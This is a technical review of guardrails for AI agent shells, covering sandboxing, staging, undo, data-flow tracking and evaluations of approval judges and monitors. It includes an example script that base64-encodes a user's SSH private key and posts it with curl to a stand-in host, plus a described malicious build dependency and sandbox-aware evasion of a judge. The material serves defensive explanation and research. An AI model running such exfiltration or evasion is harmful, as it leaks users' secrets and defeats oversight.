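Konstantinou and colleagues think tests generated from the description alone probably caught more faults because the quality of their expected results was higher, although they did not measure this directly. Line coverage didn't explain the difference, since these tests ran between 96% and 99% of the lines in the programs and most of the other methods came close to that. The number of tests didn't explain it either. In many cases, tests from the description made the faulty program behave differently from the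 correct one less often than other tests did, yet they still caught more faults.

The detection rates are low partly because the faults were chosen to be hard to find and the models were mostly small or inexpensive. The tasks were short Python problems, which have little in common with a script that rearranges a disk. The comparison between the two workflows should apply to shell scripts better than the percentages do, because a model that writes tests for its own shell script also has the faulty code in its context.

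*Beyond Coverage and Mutation* (Shi and Luo, 2026) examined 14,320 tests written by four models and found that 19.7% failed to run successfully. Of the test failures, 15.6% involved a wrong expected result. The working tests mostly used normal inputs and left unusual values unchecked. For the Vim script, such tests would cover cases with and without a swap file, but not `swp` or `-old.txt`.

*How well LLM-based test generation techniques perform with newer LLM versions?* (2026), an earlier study by Konstantinou, Degiovanni and Papadakis, found only about 40% to 50% of tests usable. When a test failed, some models wrote new code to replace part of the program under test. In a shell, the equivalent would be a test that replaces `rm` with a harmless imitation and then reports that no files were lost.

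Wrong expectations were also the most common fault in *Quality Assessment of Python Tests Generated by Large Language Models* (2025), which counted 151 errors in tests from three coding assistants. Asking the same model to check its tests only partly helps. In *Coding Triangle* (2025), models recognized some of their own incorrect test cases, but when they misjudged a test case, they usually accepted a wrong one.

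The older methods of generating tests are not clearly better. *Test Wars* (2025) compared model-written tests with tests from symbolic execution and from search programs that improve tests by trial and error. According to Konstantinou and colleagues' summary, the model-written tests could do better at detecting small faults that the researchers had planted. A shell could use both kinds of method, with a solver to find unusual directories and a model to suggest what should happen in them.

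The Python results suggest that the model should write those expectations in a new conversation that contains the user's request but not the script. It may still misread the request in the same way, but where the two readings differ, a failed test is useful because it can show the user that the request was ambiguous. If the request is to delete all log files, for example, the script might skip subdirectories while a test expects the log files there to be deleted. Neither is necessarily wrong, and the user can then decide whether to include subdirectories, which they had not thought to specify.

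### A test that deleted a home directory

Tests of a script that deletes files are themselves dangerous. In August 2026, the developer Sebastien Guillemot lost his home directory to a test meant to show that a script could not delete it.

Guillemot (2026) reports in *Bad news* that his coding agents were filling the disk with temporary files in `/tmp`. He asked Claude Fable to give each agent its own space there that would be cleared automatically. Fable proposed a script that would first check whether an agent was still running. Guillemot found it too complicated, and Fable started a critical review of the design without being asked. The review triggered Anthropic's safety classifier twice, which switched the session to Opus 5 and then to Opus 4.8.

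Opus 4.8 correctly identified that a symbolic link in `/tmp` could lead the cleanup to files elsewhere on the disk. It wrote a deletion script meant to work only inside `/tmp`, and tested the script by telling it to delete the home directory. The script deleted the home directory and left the junk in `/tmp`.

Accounts differ on which step failed. Guillemot writes that the safe script didn't work, and Dagens PS's *AI-assistenten skulle städa datorn*, a Swedish press report based on his posts, repeats this. According to Tom's Hardware, the check correctly flagged the home directory as dangerous, but the test's cleanup step used the same variable name and deleted the directory. Tom's Hardware puts the loss at 700 GB and a week's work. Guillemot recovered much of it from GitHub and by having Codex piece together fragments on the disk.

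On either account, the idea behind the test was reasonable, because a safeguard against deleting the home directory needs a test that tries to delete one. The mistake was using the real home directory, since the test has to be harmless if the safeguard fails.

A script tested on copied files can still reach the originals. In the September case that TechRadar reported, the test copy contained junctions that led back to the live files. Setting the variable `HOME` to an empty folder can also fail to protect the real home folder, because a script may contain its full path.

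On Linux, an overlay that includes every directory the script can reach will keep the script's changes in a temporary layer, even if the script follows a link or uses a full path. The test also needs to block network access, or each run will repeat any requests the script makes.

Gyawali and colleagues plan to run the tests in NaSh's sandbox, but the inverse overlay they propose for ordinary commands is poorly suited to testing. It changes the real files and restores them afterward, so Guillemot's test would have temporarily removed the real home directory, along with the settings and open files of every running program. An ordinary overlay would have left the directory in place, and the test would have needed no cleanup code.

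## Network calls, secrets and other effects that cannot be undone

An overlay can protect files because the shell controls both the old version and the new one. An external effect, such as a payment or a sent message, changes something the shell doesn't control. If a command uploads a customer list and the user then rejects its changes, the shell can restore every file on the disk, but the list stays on the computer that received it. Zhong and colleagues write that "a leaked credential cannot be unread", so the user can only replace it and hope that nobody has used it yet.

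Stopping another process causes a similar problem on the user's own machine. To stop its test server, an agent might run `pkill node`, which stops every program called `node` that the user owns. The user can restart the others, but any data those programs held only in memory is lost.

A shell can hold back an email until the user has reviewed it, as it does with staged files, because a script rarely needs an answer to one. It can't do this with every request, because a script can't process downloaded data until it arrives. Downloads can also leak secrets, since the web address in the request can contain private data.

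### Blocked unless the user agrees

Gyawali and colleagues want NaSh to prevent external effects unless the user permits them. Each command would run in new network, user and process namespaces, so it could not access networks or processes outside the sandbox. For example, `pkill node` would leave the user's other servers running.

The user could exempt individual commands in a script, such as one that downloads a public dataset. The exemption is all or nothing, so a command allowed to download the dataset could also upload the user's SSH key.

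On Linux, a command in a closed network namespace can still communicate with other programs on the same machine through socket files. Docker listens on such a file, so a command that can open it may be able to start a container with full network access. The shell has to hide these files as well.

### Seeing what a call contains

For finer control, Gyawali and colleagues propose asking the user before each API call, a request that a program makes to a service. The shell must be able to read the request, but it can't do this by monitoring system calls, because programs usually encrypt their requests before passing them to the operating system. NaSh would therefore allow calls only through accepted tools, such as `curl` or Python's `requests` library, where it can read the address and arguments before encryption.

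This would exclude much of what coding agents do, because `git`, `npm` and `cargo` make their own connections. The shell would need a description of each tool's requests, or the user would have to grant the tool unrestricted access again. The shell must also stop other programs from connecting directly, which it could do by keeping the network namespace closed and having the accepted tools pass their requests to a helper outside it.

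### Following an SSH key

Even when the shell can read the arguments, they may not show where the data came from. Consider this script:

```
key=$(cat ~/.ssh/id_rsa)
report=$(echo "$key" | base64)
curl -d "$report" https://stats.example.com/build
```

The script reads the user's private key, encodes it with `base64`, and sends the result to an address that looks like a service for build statistics. Because of the encoding, the user would see a long string of letters and digits, and a filter that searched the request for the text of the key would not find it.

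Information flow control follows the data instead. Every piece of data carries a label that lists the files it came from, and each command's output receives the labels of all its inputs:

label(output) = label(input 1) ∪ label(input 2) ∪ …

| Step | Data | Label |
|---|---|---|
| `cat` reads the key | `key` | `~/.ssh/id_rsa` |
| `base64` rewrites it | `report` | `~/.ssh/id_rsa` |
| `curl` is about to send it | body of the request | `~/.ssh/id_rsa` |

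The shell can then warn the user that the request contains data from their SSH key, or refuse to send it. Gyawali and colleagues would use command annotations to determine which outputs depend on which inputs. For a command without an annotation, the shell has to guess. If it assumes that the output depends on every file the command could read, most requests will soon trigger warnings. If it assumes no dependence, it can send the key undetected.

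Data can also leak without appearing in the request:

`grep -q Ana ~/clients.txt && curl https://stats.example.com/build`

A command might contact a server only if Ana is on a client list stored in a file. The request contains nothing from the file, but whoever runs the server learns that she is a client. To catch this leak, the shell has to label calls whose execution depends on the file, as well as calls that send its contents.

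In a coding agent, the model may also read a key in one command's output and type it into the next command, which then doesn't mention the file the key came from. To catch this, the harness would have to treat everything the model writes after reading a secret as possibly containing it.

*Cordon* (Chen, Dong and colleagues, 2026) presents a working prototype that tracks data across an agent's tool calls, including summaries the model writes. The prototype holds external actions in an outbox until it has checked the whole task. In one example, an agent investigates an outage, reads logs that contain a secret key, summarizes them and prepares a Slack message for the team. Each step looks routine, but Cordon's records show that the message derives from data containing a secret. The researchers don't claim to prove noninterference, the property that secrets do not influence anything outsiders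 can see.

In a test, Cordon stopped all 45 risky workflows before they did harm. Strategies modeled on existing defenses stopped 14, missed 26 and detected 5 too late. The comparison favors Cordon, because Chen and colleagues wrote the workflows around the kinds of risk its rules cover and built the competing strategies themselves. When the user approved everything, the average task took 31.4 seconds instead of 25.6, with an average of one approval per workflow. On subsets of two ordinary benchmarks, agents did at least as well with Cordon as without it. Cordon can't check plugins whose effects it can't observe.

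### Four downloads, one question

A request can be hard to understand even when it contains no secrets:

`curl -X DELETE 'https://api.example.com/v1/volumes/42?snapshots=all'`

Gyawali and colleagues suggest using the service's documentation to describe the request in plain words. Here the user might read "Delete storage volume 42 and all its backups." An expert could overlook the last part of the raw request, and a beginner probably couldn't read any of it. The description is only as accurate as the documentation, which a hostile service could falsify, so the shell should always show the service's address too.

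Asking about every call would soon lead to approval fatigue, so NaSh would batch the questions. When a script reaches an API call, the shell skips it, along with any code that depends on its result, and runs whatever else it can. It asks the user only when everything left is waiting for a call. Gyawali and colleagues say that a data-analysis script with four API calls would need just one question. This smaller script shows how that could work:

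```
1  mkdir -p weather
2  curl -o weather/2022.csv https://data.example.org/2022.csv
3  curl -o weather/2023.csv https://data.example.org/2023.csv
4  curl -o weather/2024.csv https://data.example.org/2024.csv
5  curl -o weather/2025.csv https://data.example.org/2025.csv
6  sort stations.txt > stations-sorted.txt
7  cat weather/*.csv > all.csv
8  wc -l all.csv
```

| Line | Before the question | After the user agrees |
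|---|---|---|
| 1 | Creates the folder | |
| 2 to 5 | Wait for permission | Download the four files |
| 6 | Sorts the list of stations, which needs no download | |
| 7 | Waits, because it reads the downloaded files | Joins them |
| 8 | Waits for line 7 | Counts the lines |

The shell would display the prompt "Download 2022.csv, 2023.csv, 2024.csv and 2025.csv from data.example.org?" To do this, it has to detect that line 7 depends on lines 2 to 5, although line 7 names none of the four files. This would require specifications of `curl` and `cat` and an analysis of the pattern `weather/*.csv`.

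Skipping works less well when one call depends on another. If the script first downloads an index with the addresses of the other files, the user has to approve that download before the shell can prompt for the rest. If each page of results contains the address of the next, the shell has to prompt the user ten times to download ten pages.

Error handling creates the same kind of dependency. Many careful scripts begin with `set -e`, which ends the script as soon as a command fails. Every later line then depends on whether the first download succeeds, so the shell can't skip ahead and this script would need four questions. The shell could instead assume that the downloads will succeed, continue, and reverse the later file changes if a download fails.

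The shell can also run a command too early. Suppose a script downloads a new version of a program and then deletes the old one. The deletion doesn't use the download's result, so the shell may delete the old version while it waits for permission to download the new one. If the user refuses, they have neither version until the shell undoes the deletion.

Batching also makes a harmful request easier to miss, since the user may not read forty addresses in one question. Grouping the addresses by service would help.

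### Undo as part of the service

Gyawali and colleagues also suggest changing the services themselves. For each operation, a service would offer an undo stub, a function its developers write to reverse that operation. With every reply, the service would send an undo context, which contains the information needed to start the reversal and any limits on it, such as a deadline.

Services often call other services, so these contexts have to be combined. Suppose a user asks the shell at noon to arrange a company lunch. The shell calls an events service, which calls a caterer's service, which calls a payment service.

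| Service | Its own undo deadline | Deadline it receives from the service it called | Deadline it returns |
|---|---|---|---|
| Payment | 14:00 today | none | 14:00 today |
| Caterer | 20:00 today | 14:00 today | 14:00 today |
| Events | 12:00 tomorrow | 14:00 today | 14:00 today |

Each service returns the earliest deadline it has, so the time left to undo everything is min(24, 8, 2) = 2 hours. The user deals only with the events service and might otherwise assume they have 24 hours.

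A single deadline leaves out useful information. At 15:00 the user could still cancel the lunch, but the payment service would no longer refund the money. Gyawali and colleagues expect similar limits from cloud services that can undo an action but not the charge for it. An undo request also takes time to pass through the chain, so the shell should stop offering a full undo shortly before 14:00. If the payment service returned no context, the other two could not guarantee that the whole order would be reversed.

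The main obstacle is that each service's developers have to write and maintain the reversals. *Robust Agent Compensation (RAC)* (Perera, Hapuarachchi and colleagues, 2026) implements a simpler version of the idea by adding a field to the tool descriptions that MCP servers give to agents. The entry for `book_flight`, for example, names `cancel_flight` as the tool that reverses it. The field cannot record a deadline or a cancellation fee.

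### GoEX: letting the model write the reversal

Patil, Zhang and colleagues (2024) argue in *GoEX* that people can judge the result of an action more easily than the code that performs it. Their system therefore lets the agent act first and gives the user a way to reverse the action, without depending on services to offer an undo.

In GoEX, developers can supply pairs of actions and reversals. If they don't, the model writes the reverse call, and GoEX records in a table called the reversion set whether the call worked. Patil and colleagues accept that the model may be "wrong at most once" for a new call. But one failed reversal may be serious, and the table improves only if someone notices the failure. The right reversal can also depend on details, such as how many Slack messages a command must delete to undo a sent message.

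GoEX can test how to reverse an action on a database or file before relying on that reversal. For a database, the model creates a small copy with the same structure, and GoEX runs the action and its reversal on the copy in a container. Some databases also let GoEX keep a transaction open until the user decides whether to keep the changes, which guarantees that GoEX can undo them but may make other users wait.

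When an action cannot be undone, GoEX limits the damage by restricting what the agent can access. For example, a user might let it read email but not send any. GoEX also keeps the user's keys in a local vault and releases a key only if the request mentions the service it belongs to. A request to send a Slack message releases the Slack key but not the bank key. The check is a simple text search, so a request that says "Don't post this on Slack" could also release the Slack key.

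Patil and colleagues also propose that services offer dry runs of their calls. Some AWS and Kubernetes commands already let users check whether a call would succeed. A preview of the resulting state would be more useful to someone deciding whether to approve the call. However, prices or other data could change between the preview and the real call.

GoEX is working software, but the main text of its paper does not report how often reversals succeed. NaSh is still a design, so the closest implementations of its ideas are in other systems.

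| Proposal | Closest built version |
|---|---|
| Block external effects by default | Agent sandboxes with a closed network |
| Trace local data into calls | Cordon |
| Skip blocked calls and batch the questions | None known |
| Undo stubs and contexts | RAC's named reversal tools, without deadlines |
| Preview the result of a remote call | Dry runs for some AWS and Kubernetes commands |

### Compensation or holding back

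*Always-On Agents* (2026), a survey, found a rollback mechanism in only 27 of the 435 works it examined. Payments and sent messages often can't be literally undone. Researchers use the term "compensation" for an action that repairs the consequences of an earlier one. *Agent libOS* (2026) describes a runtime that records how reversible each external action is but requires separate authorization for any compensation.

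RAC logs every tool call an agent makes. If a call fails, RAC retries it, then looks for another tool that could do the job. If that fails too, RAC reverses all the earlier calls, starting with the latest. In simulated airline customer service, agents succeeded in 97% of cases with RAC and 82% without it. SagaLLM, an older system that plans its reversals in advance, also reached 97%.

In a harder test, the agent was asked to book flights for three people, but the third booking always failed, so the agent had to cancel the other two. With the model Gemini 2.5 Flash, RAC succeeded in two of three runs, while the same kind of agent without RAC failed all three. With the stronger GPT-5.4, both failed every time. Three runs are too few to compare the methods precisely, but users clearly couldn't rely on RAC here.

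RAC also assumes that any tool it can't find a reversal for has no side effects. Perera and colleagues chose this rule because harmless operations such as `print` would otherwise cause errors. But an email tool may have no reversal either, and RAC would then treat a sent email as if it had changed nothing.

*Atomix* (Mohammadi, Potamitis and colleagues, 2026) avoids this problem by sorting actions before they happen. When an agent books a holiday, Atomix reserves the hotel at once because it can cancel the reservation later. It holds the confirmation email until the whole booking succeeds, and meanwhile tells the agent that the email is queued. In one experiment, the researchers aborted tasks in five ways and counted how many emails went out that should not have.

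| Method | Unwanted emails sent, out of 500 |
|---|---|
| Atomix holds the email until the task succeeds | 0 |
| Restart from a saved checkpoint | 200 |
| Atomix with the email classified wrongly | 300 |
| Compensation after sending | 400 |
| No protection | 500 |

All the methods sent the 500 emails they should have sent. The round numbers come from running each of the five failures 100 times, and a method apparently either leaked every time or never did. The experiment therefore gives evidence about only five situations. Two other methods that held emails back also leaked none, so this protection isn't unique to Atomix.

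Atomix had less of an advantage at recovering from errors. When each call had a 30% chance of a fault, it completed 17 of 30 online-shop tasks cleanly, compared with 16 for restarting from a checkpoint. Atomix also can't make two irreversible actions succeed or fail together. If it sends an email and then a payment fails, the email has still been sent.

A shell must establish whether an action happened before it can choose the right repair. *Evidence-Guided Recovery for AI Agents with Ambiguous Tool Outcomes and Partial Execution* (Zhu, Chen and colleagues, 2026) examines what an agent should do after a timeout. If the connection breaks while a service is creating an invoice, the invoice may already exist, appear a minute later, or never exist. Sending the request again could create a second invoice. Some services accept an idempotency key, a unique code that lets them recognize a repeated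 request. Without a key, a retry may be unsafe even if the shell finds no invoice, because the first request may still be in progress.

In simulations, Zhu and colleagues compared agents that got advice from a planning program with agents that saw only the available evidence. The advised agents safely completed 30 of 58 tasks, compared with 9 for the others. The planner had a list of every possible outcome, including how long each might take. A shell would rarely have such a list for a real service.

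### When "reversible" is not enough

Calling an action reversible usually means that another action can restore some part of the earlier state. That can leave a lot unchanged:

| Action | Reversal | What may remain |
|---|---|---|
| Post a chat message | Delete it | People have read or copied it |
| Start a cloud server | Delete it | The provider charges for the time it ran, or for a disk left behind |
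| Reserve a hotel room | Cancel it | The hotel keeps a fee |
| Publish a secret key | Replace it | Someone has already used it |
| Stop a process | Restart it | Unsaved data in memory is gone |

A test that compares the state before an action with the state after its reversal can miss effects that occurred in between. For example, a test that checks only whether a chat message is gone will pass even if a hundred people read the message before it was deleted. Zhu and colleagues therefore check the history of actions as well as the final state. Mohammadi and colleagues classify a reservation with a cancellation fee as "reversible with cost" and acknowledge that outsiders may see an action before Atomix reverses it.

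Other people or agents may also act on a change before it is reversed. If the hotel gives the user's preferred room to someone else after a mistaken cancellation, booking again won't get that room back. *A Five-Plane Reference Architecture for Runtime Governance of Production AI Agents* (2026) notes that when several agents work at once, reversing one agent's actions may require coordination with the others.

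A shell should show the user who may see an action, how long they can reverse it, what reversing it requires and what will remain afterwards. If the shell can't determine this, it should treat the action as irreversible and ask first. Asking will sometimes interrupt the user and delay a harmless email, but the shell can't take back an email it should not have sent.

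## Combining the guardrails and measuring whether they work

In a shell with several guardrails, one may catch what another misses, but each adds a delay or a question for the user. The request to delete the log files in `/logs` is a good test of how much the guardrails overlap, because it doesn't specify which files count as log files.

### 400 files in `/logs`

Suppose `/logs` belongs to a small online shop and holds 400 files that take up 8 GB.

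| Files | Number | Size |
|---|---|---|
| Current logs at the top, such as `app.log` | 20 | 1.0 GB |
| Renamed older copies, such as `app.log.1` | 140 | 4.2 GB |
| Hidden logs, such as `.system.log` | 4 | 0.2 GB |
| Logs in subdirectories, such as `web/access.log` | 235 | 2.6 GB |
| `README` | 1 | almost nothing |

One of the 235 files in subdirectories, `shop/orders.log`, is the shop's only record of this month's orders. The owner has forgotten about it and wants to free some space. The model writes `find /logs -name '*.log' -delete`, which deletes 259 files and 3.8 GB. The command misses the renamed copies, which take up more than half the space, and deletes the record of the orders.

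| Guardrail | What it catches | What passes | What the owner sees | Cost |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Check on the command's text | Nothing, unless a rule covers `find -delete` | All 259 deletions | The command, if the rule asks | Under 1 ms, perhaps 1 question |
| Confinement | Mistakes outside `/logs`, of which there are none | All 259 deletions | A request for write access to `/logs` | 1 question |
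| Closed network | Nothing, since the command contacts nobody | All 259 deletions | Nothing | Almost none |
| Staging | It holds back every deletion until the owner decides | Nothing yet | Nothing yet | About 0.2 seconds |
| Effect summary | `orders.log`, if the owner spots it | The 140 copies, which aren't on the list | 259 deletions, grouped by directory | 1 question and some reading |
| Undo after the commit | `orders.log`, if the owner misses it later | Orders missed until the old version is gone | A way to restore it | Up to 3.8 GB of disk space |
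| Generated tests, if the owner keeps the script | The renamed copies | `orders.log` | 3 questions about example files | A few short runs |

The summary is the owner's first chance to notice the orders. If it groups the subdirectory logs as 180 in `web`, 54 in `api` and 1 in `shop`, the owner may spot the last entry. A message that only reported 259 deleted logs would hide it. The summary doesn't list the 140 older copies, because the command didn't change them, but a line such as "frees 3.8 of 8.0 GB" would show the owner that something is left.

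If each guardrail requires its own confirmation, the owner answers three questions before the shell deletes any files. The question about the command is the least useful, and a shell that stages changes can drop it because the real files don't change until the owner accepts the summary.

Keeping old versions for undo works against a request to free disk space, because those versions still take up space. A shell could discard the largest old versions first, which would free nearly all of the 3.8 GB and still let it restore a small file like `orders.log`.

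Staging has a problem here too, because the shop keeps writing to the real files while the owner reads the summary. A new order may arrive, for example. The shell should check for such changes before it commits, but the current logs change all the time, so the check would mostly raise false alarms.

If the owner saves the command as a monthly script, the shell could test it on directories that contain a subdirectory, a hidden log and a renamed copy. Three yes-or-no answers are enough to choose among the eight readings of the request. The tests probably won't include a list of orders, because neither the request nor the script mentions one.

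### A hostile build

Suppose an agent runs the `cargo build` from the earlier example by Zhong and colleagues, and the malicious dependency reads the SSH key and also edits the user's shell configuration.

A check on the command's text lets it through because the command is routine, so the protection here comes mostly from confinement. A rule that blocks reads of `~/.ssh` or requires approval for them protects the key, and blocking network access prevents a stolen key from leaving the machine. The build may need the network to fetch packages, so the harness should download them first and then build offline.

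Staging holds back the edit to the shell configuration. The summary can show that edit if the shell lists changes outside the project before the compiled files. The summary can't show that the script read the key, so the shell also needs a record of blocked reads. Generated tests would only run the hostile script again.

The build script could get past every guardrail by hiding malicious code in the compiled program, which belongs in the project and looks like the expected result. The code would then run with the user's full access when the user starts the program outside the sandbox. Confinement is still the most important guardrail for the build, but accepting the changes may be a mistake even when the list of files is right. Confinement hardly helps with the logs, where the summary matters most.

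### The YoloFS evaluation

Most agent benchmarks bypass approval prompts, so they can't measure how often an agent interrupts its user. Zhong and colleagues built a test program that operates each agent through a simulated terminal, as a person would. It types the request, checks the screen for permission prompts and answers them by a fixed rule. Each task starts in a fresh directory and has a three-minute limit. At the end, the program compares the files with the expected result.

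The program ran both sets of tasks mentioned earlier, the 11 with hidden damage and the 112 routine ones.

| Setup | Model | 11 tasks with hidden damage | Routine tasks completed | Questions per routine task |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code with YoloFS | Claude Sonnet 4.6 | Undid the damage in 8, left it staged in 3 | 99% | 0.4 |
| Claude Code | Claude Sonnet 4.6 | Damage in 10, asked in 1 | 98% | 0.9 |
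| Codex | GPT-5.3-Codex | Asked in all 11 | 100% | 0.4 |
| Copilot CLI | Claude Sonnet 4.6 | Damage in 10, asked in 1 | 96% | 1.3 |
| Gemini CLI | Gemini 3 Flash preview | Damage in 9, failed to run the command in 2 | 75% | 2.2 |

The researchers hid the damage in four ways. Three tasks used a readable script, three used a makefile that called another script, two used longer chains, and three used compiled programs without source code. Nobody told Claude to look for damage in YoloFS's summaries.

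In one task, Claude saw that a linter, a tool that checks code for mistakes, had deleted two files. Claude considered this unusual and went back. In another task, a packaging command deleted the source code, the README and the license. Claude restored them, then traced the cause through three levels of scripts.

The three tasks it got wrong were a deployment that deleted the original source code, an installation that reset two settings files, and a repair tool that overwrote `config.json` and `settings.yaml`. Claude read both of the repair tool's files and decided the changes "appear to be expected validation fixes". One task used a readable script, one a makefile and one a compiled program, so concealment doesn't explain the failures. In each case, the damage resembled what the user had asked for. Deleting `orders.log` when asked to delete logs is the same kind of mistake.

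With only 11 tasks, 8 successes are compatible with a true success rate anywhere from about 43% to 90%.

In the routine tasks, YoloFS never prompted the user about work inside the project. It prompted the user 0.9 times per task about paths outside the project and 0.8 times about links that led outside it. Most of Gemini's failures came from a built-in rule that forbids access outside the project, so a strict guardrail can make an agent look incompetent.

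YoloFS's speed was close to that of an ordinary filesystem, as the earlier comparison with OverlayFS showed. Commit time grows in proportion to the number of snapshots. The measurements cover time but not disk space.

The evaluation leaves several things untested:

- All 11 tasks in the first set contained damage, so the results don't show how often Claude would undo a legitimate change.
- No person reviewed the three damaged results that Claude accepted.
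- The projects in the first set had between 10 and 41 lines of code, so the summaries were short.
- The hostile build was an example, and no task in either set measured whether a user would refuse to give a malicious program a secret.
- The researchers tested YoloFS only with Claude Code and one model, although it also supports Copilot and Gemini.

### Letting a second model read the summary

In *Shall We Approve?* (October 2026), Wu, Chen and colleagues independently test YoloFS against other systems, including CARE, Claude Code's automatic approval mode and their own, CAPER.

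CAPER takes a snapshot of a container, runs the command there without network access, and records what the command does. It condenses the record into a short report of changed files, attempted connections, output and reads of secrets. A separate model compares the report with the user's request. If the model approves, CAPER keeps the result. Otherwise, it restores the snapshot and sends the agent the reason.

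The researchers extended the YoloFS tasks to 102 dangerous ones, in which a tool secretly deletes or overwrites a file. Each has a safe version with the same request and command but a harmless tool, so blocking the safe version is always a mistake. They also used 682 tasks from SABER, a benchmark in which an ordinary development request can lead to a specific harm, such as a leaked key.

| System | Extended YoloFS tasks: harmed | Completed safely | Safe twins blocked | SABER: harmed | Completed safely |
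|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| No approval | 71.6% | 17.6% | none | 19.7% | 57.4% |
| CARE | 69.6% | 15.7% | 2.0% | 15.0% | 47.9% |
| Claude Code's automatic mode | 62.7% | 7.8% | 3.9% | 14.8% | 44.0% |
| YoloFS | 35.3% | 22.5% | none | 21.2% | 54.1% |
| CAPER | 7.8% | 60.8% | 1.0% | 6.7% | 48.6% |
| CAPER inside Claude Code | 6.9% | 40.2% | 2.0% | 10.0% | 45.5% |

With YoloFS, the agent went back in 66 of the 102 dangerous tasks, or 65%, close to its rate in the original 11. Of the other 36 runs, 33 ended in harm. The test apparently counted changes as harm if the agent kept them, without giving a user the chance to reject them at the end, so YoloFS would probably do better with an attentive user.

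On SABER, YoloFS did slightly worse than no approval. Wu and colleagues attribute this to credentials that an agent had already sent, which a rollback cannot recall. But the difference is about 10 of 682 tasks and could be due to chance, especially since the two setups used different harnesses and ran each task only once.

The researchers conclude that a judge other than the agent should review changes before the commit. The need for a separate judge is less certain than it looks. CAPER's judge was GPT-5.6 Luna, while YoloFS relied on the agent's own model, GLM-5.3-Flash. When the researchers replaced CAPER's judge with a weaker model, harm rose to 33.3%, about the same as with YoloFS. Much of CAPER's advantage may therefore come from the quality of its judge rather than the judge's independence.

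The evidence for running the command first is stronger. When the judge only predicted the effects from the command and the files it mentioned, harm fell to 3.9%, but the judge blocked 61.8% of the safe twins. It blocked only 1.0% of them when it was given the observed effects. Showing the judge which lines had changed also helped, since harm rose from 7.8% to 13.7% without that information.

The judge typically took 3.2 seconds per command, and the sandbox added about half a second. Together they would add roughly 18 minutes to a session of 300 commands. The tests did not include an attacker who adapted to CAPER, for example by using a tool that behaves well when it detects the sandbox. CAPER also checks only shell commands, so the harness's own file-editing tools need a separate guardrail.

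### Six measures that a builder should report

A guardrail can prevent harm, help the user notice it or make it reversible, but it always has some drawback. The six measures below cover these effects. Each resembles another measure that is easier to obtain but makes the shell look better than it is.

| Measure | How to count it | Misleading version |
|---|---|---|
| Harmful effects that reached real files or left the machine | Share of dangerous tasks that end with damage | Number of blocked commands |
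| Effects the user failed to notice | Share of planted harmful changes that people accept | Users' confidence, or how often they approve |
| Questions per session | Every prompt in a full working session | Prompts per one-step task |
| Legitimate work blocked | Harmless tasks that the guardrail stops or delays | Share of safe single commands blocked |
| Time and disk cost | Seconds added per command and space held until the commit | A percentage on one small project |
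| Success of recovery | Share of planted damage that undo fully repairs | Share of rollbacks that run without error |

The number of blocked commands is misleading because a shell that refused everything would score perfectly. When Liu and colleagues ran 600 model-written commands for harmful tasks, the safety model Granite Guardian reduced the share that succeeded from 75% to 26%, the lowest share with any guard they tested. But it also refused 131 of 300 legitimate requests.

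Refusals add up when an agent can try again, an effect that tests of single commands can't measure. In a version of the test with up to five turns per task, Granite Guardian refused 529 commands, and the agent completed 49% of the tasks instead of 65%.

Combining outcome categories can also hide lost work. On SABER, safe completions fell from 57.4% without approval to 48.6% with CAPER, while the share of tasks where the agent refused or stopped to ask rose from 9.1% to 19.1%. The "safe outcomes" category counts both, so it rose slightly, from 66.6% to 67.8%. Some of the refusals were surely right, but the combined figure doesn't show how many.

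YoloFS's *Benchmark methodology and results*, a page on the project's website, reports that Claude Code with YoloFS caught the damage in 11 of 11 tasks and that Codex caught it in none. The 11 include three cases that Claude accepted, because the user could still reject them. Codex also left the decision to the user in all 11 tasks but got no credit for it. YoloFS users do have better information, since Codex shows only the command. But the test had no real users to catch anything, and the paper is clearer because it separates the other 8 cases from these 3.

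Approval rates are poor evidence of what users notice. Wu and colleagues cite Anthropic's figure that users approve 93% of Claude Code's permission prompts. This could mean that nearly all the commands were fine or that users had stopped reading the prompts. To find out, a builder has to plant harmful changes among harmless ones and see whether users reject them.

The number of questions per task can mislead in a similar way. YoloFS and Codex both averaged 0.4 on the routine tasks, but YoloFS asked the user about paths and Codex asked about whole commands. A shell that never asks would score zero, so the number is only meaningful alongside the harm the shell allowed.

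*Fault-Tolerant Sandboxing for AI Coding Agents* (Yan, 2025) describes a prototype that blocks forbidden commands and takes a snapshot before uncertain ones. The paper reports that the prototype succeeded in all 20 attempts in each of four categories. Even a system that failed one time in eight would pass all 20 about 7% of the time, if the attempts were independent.

The larger problem is that the prototype restores the snapshot only if the command reports an error, so its perfect recovery rate covers only commands that report one. Because the `find` command that deletes the orders reports success, the prototype would discard the snapshot and make the loss permanent.

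The same paper reports a 14.5% slowdown, but its measurements of 4.69 seconds without the prototype and 6.51 seconds with it amount to 39%. Most of the extra time is spent copying a 250 MB project. Copying the 8 GB in `/logs` at that rate would take about a minute before every such command.

An undo log can also make recovery look more successful than it is. *Building Effective AI Coding Agents for the Terminal* describes a log that drops its oldest entries when it reaches a maximum length and never records changes made by shell commands. A test that undid only the logged changes could show near-perfect recovery. A fair test would damage files in several ways, let the agent continue working, attempt recovery, and then compare every file with its original.

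### Combinations that nobody has tested

Builders can't estimate the remaining harm simply by multiplying results from separate tests. CARE caught 76% of the dangerous commands in its own main test. If it had caught the same share in the extended YoloFS tasks, harm would have fallen from 71.6% to about 17%. It fell only to 69.6%, because the damage came from tools that the commands started, and CARE reads only the commands. Two guardrails can also fail on the same cases. For example, the agent, the second model and the user may all miss a harmful change that looks like part of the task.

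A combination therefore needs its own test, and few have had one:

| Combination | Tested on | What the test left out |
|---|---|---|
| YoloFS: staging, summaries and questions about file access | 123 tasks by its developers; 784 dangerous tasks by others | People who review the changes |
| CAPER: rollback, effects report, second model, closed network | The same 784 tasks, and 102 safe twins | People, adaptive attackers, a real network |
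| Yan's prototype: command filter and rollback | 10 scenarios | Wrong commands that report success |
| ShellVis: staging and changes shown line by line | 7 experienced users | A comparison group and beginners |
| AgentRewind: restored files and restored conversation | 171 tasks | Whether it prevents harm |

No published evaluation appears to combine staging, effect summaries and generated tests. Gyawali and colleagues proposed summaries and generated tests for NaSh, with an inverse overlay instead of staging, but did not measure any of these parts. They note that each part could work separately. If so, researchers could add them one at a time and measure what each contributes.

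Such an experiment could give the same requests to four versions of a shell: one with staging alone, one with summaries added, one with generated tests added, and one with both added. It would need harmful tasks, each paired with a similar safe one. It would also need to rerun each saved script on new files, because a generated test can only show a benefit on a later run.

The study would also need about 430 dangerous tasks for each version to detect a drop in harm from 10% to 5% with the usual statistical standards. Agents could do this in a few days. People would tire and probably stop reading after several hundred summaries, so a study with human reviewers would need many participants who each judge a small number.
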